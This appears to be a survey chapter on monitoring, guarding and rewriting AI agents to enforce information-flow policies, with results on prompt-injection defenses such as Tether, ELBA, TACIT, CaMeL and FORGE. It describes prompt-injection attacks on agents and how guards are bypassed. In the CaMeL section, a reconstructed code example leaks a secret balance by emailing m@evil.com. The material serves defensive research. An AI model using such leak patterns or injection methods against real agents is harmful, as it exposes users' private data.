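Even a perfect judge can't enforce some policies by examining one run at a time. *Local Allow, Global Deny* (Pandey, Jain and colleagues, 2026) gives the example of an assistant that schedules a team meeting. It may tell others when the user is free or busy, but what it tells them must not depend on *why* the user is busy. Suppose the user is free at 10 and 11. The assistant offers 10 if another slot contains an ordinary meeting, and 11 if that slot contains a confidential interview. Each offer is harmless by itself, but someone who knows the pattern can infer from an offer of 11 that there is an interview.

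The policy is a hyperproperty, a form of noninterference that allows some private information to affect the output. For any two runs *t* and *t′*, it requires:

low(*t*) = low(*t′*) and *D*(hi(*t*)) = *D*(hi(*t′*)) ⇒ *α*(obs(*t*)) = *α*(obs(*t′*)).

Here low is the declared purpose and other public input, hi is the private context, and obs is what the assistant discloses. The function *D* selects the private information that the purpose allows the assistant to use, here the free and busy times. The function *α* selects the parts of the disclosure that matter, such as which slots the assistant offers.

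Pandey and colleagues prove that a monitor that sees only single runs and never raises a false alarm detects no violation of this policy. A single run always satisfies the formula, because it discloses the same things as itself, so it could have come from a compliant assistant. For instance, an assistant that always offers 11 would produce the same run when there is an interview. A monitor without false alarms therefore has to accept every run.

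Random choices make the problem harder. An assistant that tosses a coin to choose between 10 and 11 may offer different times in two runs without revealing anything. The policy should therefore require that the *probability* of each disclosure not depend on the private reason. Pandey and colleagues show that a single run still can't establish whether an agent meets this requirement, because any run could have come from either a safe agent or a leaking one. Comparing many runs provides statistical evidence but never certainty, because a leak can be too small to detect in any given number of runs.

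Nine language models also served as judges on ten versions of the scheduling example, with three repetitions of each. When the judges saw one action at a time, eight of them never blocked the leaking assistant. The ninth, Kimi-K2.6, blocked it in 3 of 30 cases, but it also blocked a harmless control in 1 of 30. All nine always blocked openly unauthorized forwarding of information. When the judges saw both runs together, eight detected the leak every time and Llama-4-Maverick detected it in 17 of 30 cases. A single run didn't contain the information needed to detect the leak, so missing it when shown one action at a time doesn't reveal a weakness in the judges.

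Pandey and colleagues tested whether a real agent leaks information this way and found no leak in 80 scheduling runs with Claude Sonnet 4.6, which suggests a rate below about 4% for that task. An early analysis seemed to show a leak, but the agent had offered the same slots in both conditions and only its wording differed.

### A monitor that can rerun the agent

This impossibility result does not contradict the 2006 model, in which a monitor can enforce some policies that compare runs because it has the program's text. The proof by Pandey and colleagues relies on a compliant assistant and a leaking one producing the same run. That cannot happen in the 2006 model, because the first event of each run identifies the program.

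A guard with the weights, the scaffolding and the calendar could replace the interview with an ordinary meeting, run the assistant again with the same random numbers and compare the offers. A difference wouldn't prove a leak, because the assistant might offer each slot half the time in both cases, with the interview changing only which random numbers lead to which slot. To rule this out, the guard would have to compute the probability of each offer. This is possible in principle if the length of the runs is limited, but there are far too many possible texts to go through. The theorem about random agents explicitly assumes that the monitor doesn't know these probabilities.

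If runs can be any length, even the program's text may not be enough. When only the eventual output matters, the scheduling policy has the same problem as the secret-file policy, because one of the two runs might take arbitrarily long to produce its offer.

*AttriGuard* (2026) describes a guard that compares runs, unlike any of the six designs that Pandey and colleagues surveyed. It protects against instructions that attackers hide in tool results. Whenever the agent proposes tool calls, AttriGuard runs the model again on a version of the context in which the tool results have less influence on it, and blocks any call that has no close match in the second run. The guard only needs to be able to run the model, not inspect its weights, but each step that proposes a call requires extra computation.

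### Guards that also block legitimate actions

A guard that sees only one run can still prevent the scheduling leak if it is allowed to make false alarms. It could apply the rule against sending a message after reading a file, and block every message once the assistant has read the reasons in the calendar. Earlier messages can't depend on reasons it hasn't read. But an assistant that starts by reading the whole calendar could then never propose a time.

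Many other policies need only a guard that keeps a record of earlier actions. Pandey and colleagues gave a calendar task to an agent built on the model Qwen3-30B. In 22 of 60 runs, the agent disclosed more in total than the user had agreed to, although each disclosure was acceptable by itself. With a guard that compared each action with the purpose of the task, the agent still disclosed too much in 20 of 60 runs. With a guard that kept track of the total, it never did, and the guard blocked nothing in 120 harmless runs.

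*NOMOS* (2026) describes a way to turn an organization's written rules into such guards. The guards record facts from tool results and user messages, never from assertions in the model's output, and check each call in microseconds without a language model. They enforce the rules exactly, including any mistakes in them.

*Tether* (Sistla, Solko-Breslin and colleagues, 2026) applies conservative tracking to coding agents, which are difficult to guard because a single command can run a script that reads files and contacts other computers. Tether runs each command in a temporary layer over the file system and holds back its network requests until it has checked them. It keeps the changes only if the policy permits everything the command did. This gives it some of the power of an edit automaton, but only within a single command.

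Tether also attaches a sensitivity label to each file. Suppose an agent uploads a public report, copies a confidential inventory into the report, and then tries to upload the report again. The two upload commands are identical, but Tether blocks the second because the report now has the inventory's label. If a script reads one file and writes another, Tether treats the second file as containing information from the first, even if it doesn't.

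The developers tested Tether on recorded runs from two benchmarks and compared it with Claude Code's Auto Mode, in which a language model reviews each command:

| Guard | Attacks blocked | Legitimate runs blocked |
|---|---|---|
| Tether | 344 of 344 (100%) | 74 of 1,590 (4.7%) |
| Auto Mode with its default rules | 315 of 344 (91.6%) | 155 of 1,590 (9.7%) |
| Auto Mode with Tether's policy | 307 of 344 (89.2%) | 55 of 1,590 (3.5%) |

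In 50 of the 74 legitimate runs that Tether blocked, the agent had edited a protected file without being asked to. In 7, it had contacted a server that the task didn't mention. In the other 17, it had read secret files, often by accident. For example, a search through every file on the computer also opens the secret ones, and Tether can't detect whether the agent used their contents.

These results probably overstate somewhat how well Tether would work in use. Sistla and colleagues refined the policy by testing it on benchmark runs, and recorded runs can't show how an agent would have reacted to a block. They also tested Tether against an agent that actively tried to get around it. The agent's success rate on ten tasks fell from 40% to zero over three versions as the developers fixed the gaps it found.

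Even a low false-alarm rate can cause many unnecessary interruptions if attacks are rare. Suppose one run in 1,000 is an attack. At Tether's measured rates, a guard would block that run and about 47 legitimate ones. A system could ask the user instead of blocking, but the user would then have to recognize the one attack among dozens of harmless requests.

The test also left out attacks that Tether can't track in detail. Sistla and colleagues estimate that 28% of runs in one benchmark and 22% in the other require a judgment about content, such as whether a change to a file the agent is allowed to edit is malicious. They suggest combining Tether with a language model for these cases, but any guarantee would then depend on the model's judgments being correct.

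## Changing an AI agent's code and scaffolding

The secret-file policy requires a program to behave exactly as it would if a certain file didn't exist. No monitor can enforce it when only the program's output matters, but a few changed lines of scaffolding can enforce it for an AI agent. Suppose the agent has a tool that lists the files in a folder:

```
def list_folder(path):
    return os.listdir(path)
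```

The rewritten tool removes the secret file's name before the model receives the list:

```
def list_folder(path):
    names = os.listdir(path)
    return [n for n in names if full_path(path, n) != SECRET]
```

If this list is the agent's only source of information about the file, the model's output can no longer depend on whether the file exists, so the rewritten agent meets RW1. An agent that would have ignored the file behaves the same way it did before, which RW2 requires.

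Nobody has to judge whether the agent would have misused the file. A guard on tool calls would have to detect, for example, that an email giving the number of files in the folder includes the secret file in that number.

### Other ways to find the file

Most agents have many other ways to detect a file. The file interface in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, by Odersky, Zhao and colleagues (2026), lets an agent's program list a folder, list everything below it, test whether a path exists, get a file's size, and read, write or delete the file. The filter has to cover all of these operations.

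An agent with a command line can bypass all of these functions by running a search command or a script. The filter then has to work at a lower level, for example by running every command in a copy of the file system without the file.

The agent's memory is another channel. *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* describes this problem in OpenClaw, a personal assistant that can serve several people. Each person has a separate conversation, but the scaffolding adds notes from a shared memory to all of them. If an administrator mentions the secret file in one conversation, a note about it may be added to another person's conversation. The rewriter has to filter these notes too, or keep a separate memory for each person.

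### Type-checking the programs an agent writes

Many agents write short programs that call several tools, instead of requesting one call at a time. Such a program is much easier to analyze than the model that wrote it, because it consists of ordinary code and is complete before it runs. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, use this to control agents that write Haskell. Their system, ELBA, works as follows:

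1. The scaffolding asks the model for a program of a particular type.
2. The type-checker checks the program. If the program has the wrong type, the scaffolding returns the error to the model, which tries again.
3. If the program passes, the scaffolding runs it. The program can call the model again, for instance to decide what to do with a search result.

In Haskell, a program's type shows which effects it can have, such as writing to a file. The scaffolding of a public calculator can therefore require a program of type Int, which produces a whole number and has no effects. If a user tells the calculator to delete all the files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5, the model might write a program that does both, but that program has a different type, so it never runs.

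Types can also restrict where data comes from. In one example, an agent may write only bibliography entries that come from DBLP, a database of computer science papers. The library puts each entry it fetches from DBLP in a "trusted" wrapper that the agent's code cannot create, and the function that writes to the bibliography accepts only wrapped entries. The agent can still sort and filter the entries. In 100 tasks, an ordinary agent with web search got the authors, year or identifier wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations, while ELBA made no such mistakes in 925 citations.

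Some checks are possible only when the program runs. To restrict an agent to one folder, ELBA gives it a value that stands for the folder, and the type-checker rejects any attempt to open a file except by extending this value with a file name. When the program runs, the library follows any links in the path and stops the program if the resulting path is outside the folder.

ELBA also uses LIO, a Haskell library that labels data by its secrecy and source. A running program has a label that covers everything it has read so far. If the program downloads a page from an unknown website, its label records that the website has influenced it, and LIO stops it from taking actions that only more trustworthy sources may influence.

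ELBA therefore combines all three mechanisms. The type-checker statically analyzes the generated program, and the path and label checks are an execution monitor. For the agent as a whole, the scaffolding acts as a rewriter, because it runs well-typed programs unchanged and replaces ill-typed ones with an error.

Zhou and colleagues prove that any property the language guarantees for ordinary well-typed programs also holds for programs that call a model in this way. The proof replaces each call with an ordinary function that queries the model, type-checks the answer and runs it. This produces an ordinary program, to which the language's guarantees already apply. Because the answer may contain further calls, the proof assumes a limit on how deeply calls nest and works up from programs with no calls. The theorem treats the model as an arbitrary computable function, so it doesn't depend on the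 weights. It also covers properties of a whole set of runs, such as noninterference, if the language guarantees them.

### A test with agents that obey every attack

The researchers tested ELBA on the Slack tasks in AgentDojo, which pair 21 legitimate tasks with 5 injected instructions. All four models resisted all 105 of the ordinary attacks even without policies, so this test couldn't show whether the policies helped. Zhou and colleagues therefore forced the model to obey. Whenever it received data containing an attack, the scaffolding removed the real task and left only that data as its prompt. With seven repetitions, each model had 735 runs without policies and 735 with them:

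| Model | Injections resisted without policies | Injections resisted with policies | Tasks completed without policies | Tasks completed with policies |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 425 | 735 | 523 | 351 |
| Opus 4.8 | 460 | 735 | 557 | 312 |
| GPT 5.4 | 621 | 735 | 558 | 338 |
| Sonnet 5 | 540 | 735 | 494 | 294 |

The policies stopped every attack, as the theorem predicts, but the share of tasks completed fell from 73% to 44% overall. The count of 735 includes a manual correction. AgentDojo scored 29 of the 2,940 protected runs as successful attacks because the agent had opened a fixed web address, but the policies allow this and it revealed nothing.

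### Letting an agent process data it cannot read

An agent may need to work with confidential data without revealing it. Odersky and colleagues built TACIT, a system that allows this by letting only side-effect-free functions touch such data. TACIT uses Scala 3, whose compiler can track capabilities, values that give a program access to something such as a file or the network. Each function's type shows which capabilities it can use.

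When the agent's program reads a confidential file, it receives the contents in a wrapper called Classified. It can apply a function to them only if the function has no capabilities:

```
secret.map(text => text.toUpperCase)
secret.map(text => { out.write(text); text })
```

The compiler accepts the first line, whose result stays in the wrapper. It rejects the second because the function writes the text to a file. If the program prints a wrapped value, the user sees the real text but the agent sees only "Classified(\*\*\*\*)". To summarize a confidential document, the program can pass it to a separate, trusted model, which returns a summary in the same kind of wrapper.

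The compiler's check is a static analysis, and TACIT adds run-time checks on which folders and servers the program uses. Hiding the printed text works like the secret-file filter, since it happens regardless of what the agent would have done with the text. TACIT protects only a file's contents, so the agent can still find out that the file exists and that it is confidential.

The developers tested TACIT with two models, each in 131 trials with the wrapper and 131 without. Most trials combined an ordinary task with an injected instruction, and 11 were direct requests for secrets, some from people who claimed to be administrators. Neither model leaked anything with the wrapper, but without it Claude Sonnet 4.6 leaked secrets in 2 trials and MiniMax M2.5 in 11. The wrapper didn't reduce the number of completed tasks. Claude completed 99% of tasks with it and 83% without it, partly because the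 unprotected agent more often ran out of time or stopped to warn the user about an attack.

Writing Scala instead of requesting tool calls also did little harm to performance. On simulated airline and retail customer service, three models scored 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points higher with TACIT. On SWE-bench Lite, a set of 300 programming problems, MiniMax M2.5 solved 125 with TACIT and 130 without it. These benchmarks show that the models can work in a typed language, but they don't measure how many tasks a strict policy would block.

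### Planning before reading untrusted data

CaMeL (2025) separates planning from untrusted data. One model writes a program from the user's request before it sees any untrusted data. Another model reads the untrusted data and extracts values from it, but cannot call tools. An interpreter runs the program, tracks where each value came from, and checks a policy before each tool call.

Suppose a user asks the agent to send a friend $50 using the payment details on the friend's website. The plan is to fetch the page, extract the account number and make the payment. An attacker who controls the page can't add a step, because the planning model never reads the page. But the attacker can change the account number, so the interpreter also has to check whether the payment depends on untrusted data.

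The separation is a change to the scaffolding, and it works for the same reason as the secret-file filter. The planning model gets the same input whatever the page contains, so the plan can't depend on the page. The interpreter's checks are an execution monitor.

A fixed plan does not always prevent attacks. *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) reports tests in which a user asked CaMeL to read a file and follow the file's instructions precisely. With the policy checks off, the planning model twice wrote a program that could call any tool the file named, and the attacks succeeded.

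Garby and colleagues also found leaks that the policy checks miss. The following program, a reconstruction of their example, reveals whether an account balance is above a threshold:

```
rich = True
tmp = True
if balance > threshold: tmp = False
if tmp: rich = False
if rich: send_email("m@evil.com", "rich!")
```

CaMeL marks a variable as secret if the program changes it in a branch that depends on a secret. If the balance is high, the program sets `tmp` to False, and CaMeL marks `tmp` as secret. The program then skips the assignment that would set `rich` to False, so `rich` stays True and unmarked, and CaMeL lets the email through. If the balance is low, `rich` becomes False and no email is sent. Whether the email is sent therefore reveals whether the balance is high, although CaMeL never marks `rich`. CaMeL tracks only the current run, so it can't mark a variable based on an assignment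 that the run skipped.

Another leak comes from code outside the interpreter, an ordinary Python loop that prompts the model for a new program when one fails. Whether the policy blocked an attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and the loop lets an attacker repeat this until they have the whole secret.

### A noninterference theorem for agents

To rule out such leaks, Garby and colleagues designed LLMbda, a small programming language for agents. Programs in LLMbda can send prompts to a model, run the code it returns, and copy or clear a conversation. Every value and conversation has a label that shows whether it is secret or untrusted, and each operation passes the labels to its results. The retry loop is part of the program, so the interpreter tracks it too.

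The researchers proved a form of noninterference for every program in the language. Because models are random, the theorem concerns probabilities. Take two starting points that differ only in data hidden from an observer. Let *μ*(*q*) and *ν*(*q*) be the probabilities that the program finishes with the visible result *q* from each of them. These may add up to less than 1, because some runs never finish or the interpreter stops them. The theorem guarantees that there is a function *ω* such that:

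*μ*(*q*) ≤ *ω*(*q*) and *ν*(*q*) ≤ *ω*(*q*) for every *q*, and the sum of all *ω*(*q*) is at most 1.

Suppose a scheduling assistant offers 10 and 11 with equal probability on an ordinary day, but offers 10 with probability 0.9 if the user has a confidential interview. Then *ω* would have to be at least 0.9 for 10 and at least 0.5 for 11, which adds up to 1.4, so the theorem rules out this assistant. If every run finishes, the two sets of probabilities have to be identical. No guard can establish this guarantee by observing single runs.

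A secret can still affect whether the program finishes. If it affects nothing else, *ω* exists, and the difference between the visible results is at most the average probability of not finishing.

The proof constructs *ω* from an imaginary version of the program that skips any computation once it involves hidden data and substitutes an empty value. This version produces each visible result at least as often as the real program. It also behaves identically from both starting points because it never uses the hidden data, so its probabilities can serve as *ω*. The proof assistant Lean checked the proof, and a further theorem links the result to the interpreter that calls the model.

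The interpreter is an execution monitor because it follows a single run and can stop it. It can enforce a hyperproperty only because it also stops some harmless programs. For example, it stops any program that adds a message to a public conversation in a branch that depends on a secret, even if both branches would add the same message.

#### Trusting data on purpose

Many legitimate tasks, such as paying a bill stored in a file, require an agent to act on untrusted data. LLMbda therefore has an "endorse" operation, which marks untrusted data as trusted. Endorsing data provably can't expose secrets, but it does let the data influence actions.

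The agent Randori decides what to endorse when it writes its plan, before it reads any real data. It tests and repairs the plan in a simulated environment, then runs the final version once with the real tools.

Randori resisted all but 2 of 1,296 attacks on AgentDojo's banking tasks, across three models. About two-thirds of the attacks were easy to resist because they needed a tool that the plan would never use, and both successful attacks were among the other 423. Both involved the same task, in which the user asked the agent to make a payment according to a file and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The agent had endorsed the contents, so the labels could not distinguish the attack from the intended use. Without endorsement, the interpreter blocked this attack.

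Without attacks, Randori completed 36 of 48 runs with GPT-5.2, 36 with Qwen3.7-plus and 31 with MiMo-v2.5. With attacks, it completed 63% of the legitimate tasks overall.

### Adding a monitor to an existing agent

ELBA, TACIT and LLMbda each require agents to write programs in a particular language. FORGE, the monitor in *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, works with existing agent software instead. It wraps the functions that frameworks such as LangChain use to run tools and the functions that send web requests in two common Python libraries. Each wrapper pauses the call, requests a decision from a separate policy engine, and continues only if the engine allows the call. Other wrappers supply the record of earlier messages and tool results that the engine checks.

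This is an inlined reference monitor, as the paper points out, but it makes far fewer changes than SASI, which considers every instruction of the program. FORGE does not change the agent's reasoning loop or weights. Inserting the monitor is a form of rewriting, but a monitor outside the agent could enforce most of the same policies.

FORGE can also add a password or access key to a web request after the request has left the agent. Since the agent never has the password or key, it can't reveal either one, and FORGE doesn't need to check for leaks.

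An agent can recover from a blocked call and finish its task. In a test with agents that research drug side effects, each agent needed approval before using a government database. Without FORGE, the agents made 40 unauthorized requests in 15 trials. With FORGE, they made none. When a call was blocked, they read the error message, obtained approval and tried again. All 15 answers were correct with and without FORGE, but FORGE increased the average trial time from 59 to 67 seconds.

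### Why agents complete fewer tasks

For agents, the useful version of RW2 is that compliant *runs* stay unchanged. The share of tasks an agent completes when nobody attacks it gives some evidence of how far each system achieves this:

| System and AgentDojo tasks | Checks off | Checks on |
|---|---|---|
| ELBA, Slack | 76.2% | 44.0% |
| CaMeL, Slack | 72.6% | 23.8% |
| CaMeL, banking | 68.8% | 37.5% |
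| FORGE with its own policy, all tasks | 83.7% | 62.5% |
| FORGE with a policy from the system FIDES, all tasks | 83.7% | 33.2% |

The ELBA and CaMeL figures combine results for several models. Many runs fail even with the checks off. ELBA's failures without policies were mostly due to the model refusing the task. The model failed to produce a well-typed program in only 7 of 2,688 runs, so the further drop in success with the checks on is mostly due to the policies.

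FORGE's results show more directly how many failed runs had a blocked call. With its own policy, about 182 of 485 runs failed. FORGE had blocked at least one call in 115 of these, though some of them might have failed anyway. The other 67 failed without a blocked call, a number similar to the 79 failures with FORGE off. With the FIDES policy, about 324 runs failed, 277 of them after a blocked call.

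The same software enforced both policies, so the large difference comes from the policies. The FIDES policy forbids important actions once the agent has read anything untrusted. FORGE's own policy allows some of them, for instance if the user named the recipient. If an agent reads an untrusted email and then pays a bill the user asked it to pay, the run violates the FIDES policy, so blocking it is consistent with RW2 for that policy. But nobody would object to the payment, so under the policy people care about, the software has blocked compliant behavior.

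In Randori's results, two models completed 67 of 96 runs with endorsement and 56 without it. Three of the 16 banking tasks require the agent to act on the contents of a file, which the interpreter blocks unless the agent endorses those contents. With so few tasks, though, chance could explain much of the difference in completed runs. The 29 failures with endorsement probably have other causes, such as the unfamiliar language.

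Some tasks can't be completed under any secure policy, so an agent's inability to complete them is not a failure of RW2. Garby and colleagues report that ELBA's developers said this was true of many of the Slack tasks.

### What the guarantees leave out

Each guarantee covers only the channels that the system controls. FORGE does not check the agent's final answer or direct network connections that bypass its wrappers. When FORGE used its own policy and an extra defense that repeatedly reminded the agent of the user's request, only 10 of 4,745 attacks succeeded. In all 10, the attacker wanted the agent to recommend a hotel, and the agent mentioned it in its final answer, which required no tool call.

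TACIT doesn't prevent leaks through timing, because even a function with no side effects can take longer for some secrets than for others. TACIT also loses control when a program starts an external command. Odersky and colleagues recommend allowing only specific, safe commands and running them in a sandbox.

The guarantees of ELBA and TACIT also require trust in the compiler and in the libraries that control access to tools, though not in the model that writes the program. Standard Haskell has a function that hides effects from the type system, so ELBA restricts agents to a safer version of the language. TACIT relies on an experimental part of the Scala compiler. Researchers have proved the underlying type system sound, but not yet the full set of restrictions that TACIT uses. Library authors can also mark code as safe when the compiler can't verify it, and a mistake there could let an agent's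 program leak secrets without a type error.

LLMbda has the strongest proof, but its theorems assume that all data sources are part of the program. The tests simulated the bank account and the files in LLMbda itself. With a real bank, someone would have to make sure that the connection labels everything correctly.

A policy can also be wrong. If a user asks an agent to delete the largest file, FORGE checks that the agent's choice is the largest in a file listing. An early form of this rule accepted any listing the agent had seen. After deleting the largest file, the agent could request a new listing and delete the next one, which was now the largest. The developers added a rule that blocks the deletion if any listing shows a different file as the largest. They also found three attacked runs in which the agent booked the most expensive hotel despite the user's price limit, which the policy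 allowed because it had no rule about prices.

### Fine-tuning

Fine-tuning trains an existing model further on new examples. It takes one program and returns another before the new one runs, so it has the form of a rewriter. But it doesn't by itself meet RW1, which requires the new program to comply on every possible input. Training makes good outputs more likely on a limited set of examples, which doesn't guarantee compliance on other inputs. Even on the training examples, the model may still have a small probability of making a forbidden tool call.

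A developer can easily guarantee that a model never produces a particular token by setting the token's probability to zero. This doesn't help with a policy such as "never pay a stranger", because the same tokens can make a forbidden payment in one context and a permitted one in another. A guarantee would need a proof about how the weights respond to every possible context, and fine-tuning doesn't provide one.

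Experience with attacks supports this. Several groups have trained models to ignore instructions hidden in data, but *Formal Policy Enforcement for Agentic Systems* notes that attackers who adapt to these defenses can get past them. Zhou and colleagues cite a similar result, in which OpenAI's automated attack system GPT-Red consistently circumvented GPT-5.5's defenses.

Fine-tuning can still make a rewritten agent more useful. If the scaffolding blocks every forbidden call, a model that rarely attempts one will complete more tasks. Training may also be the best available way to improve the agent's final answers, which most of these systems don't check. Because the theorem about ELBA holds for any model, developers can fine-tune or replace the model without proving the guarantee again.
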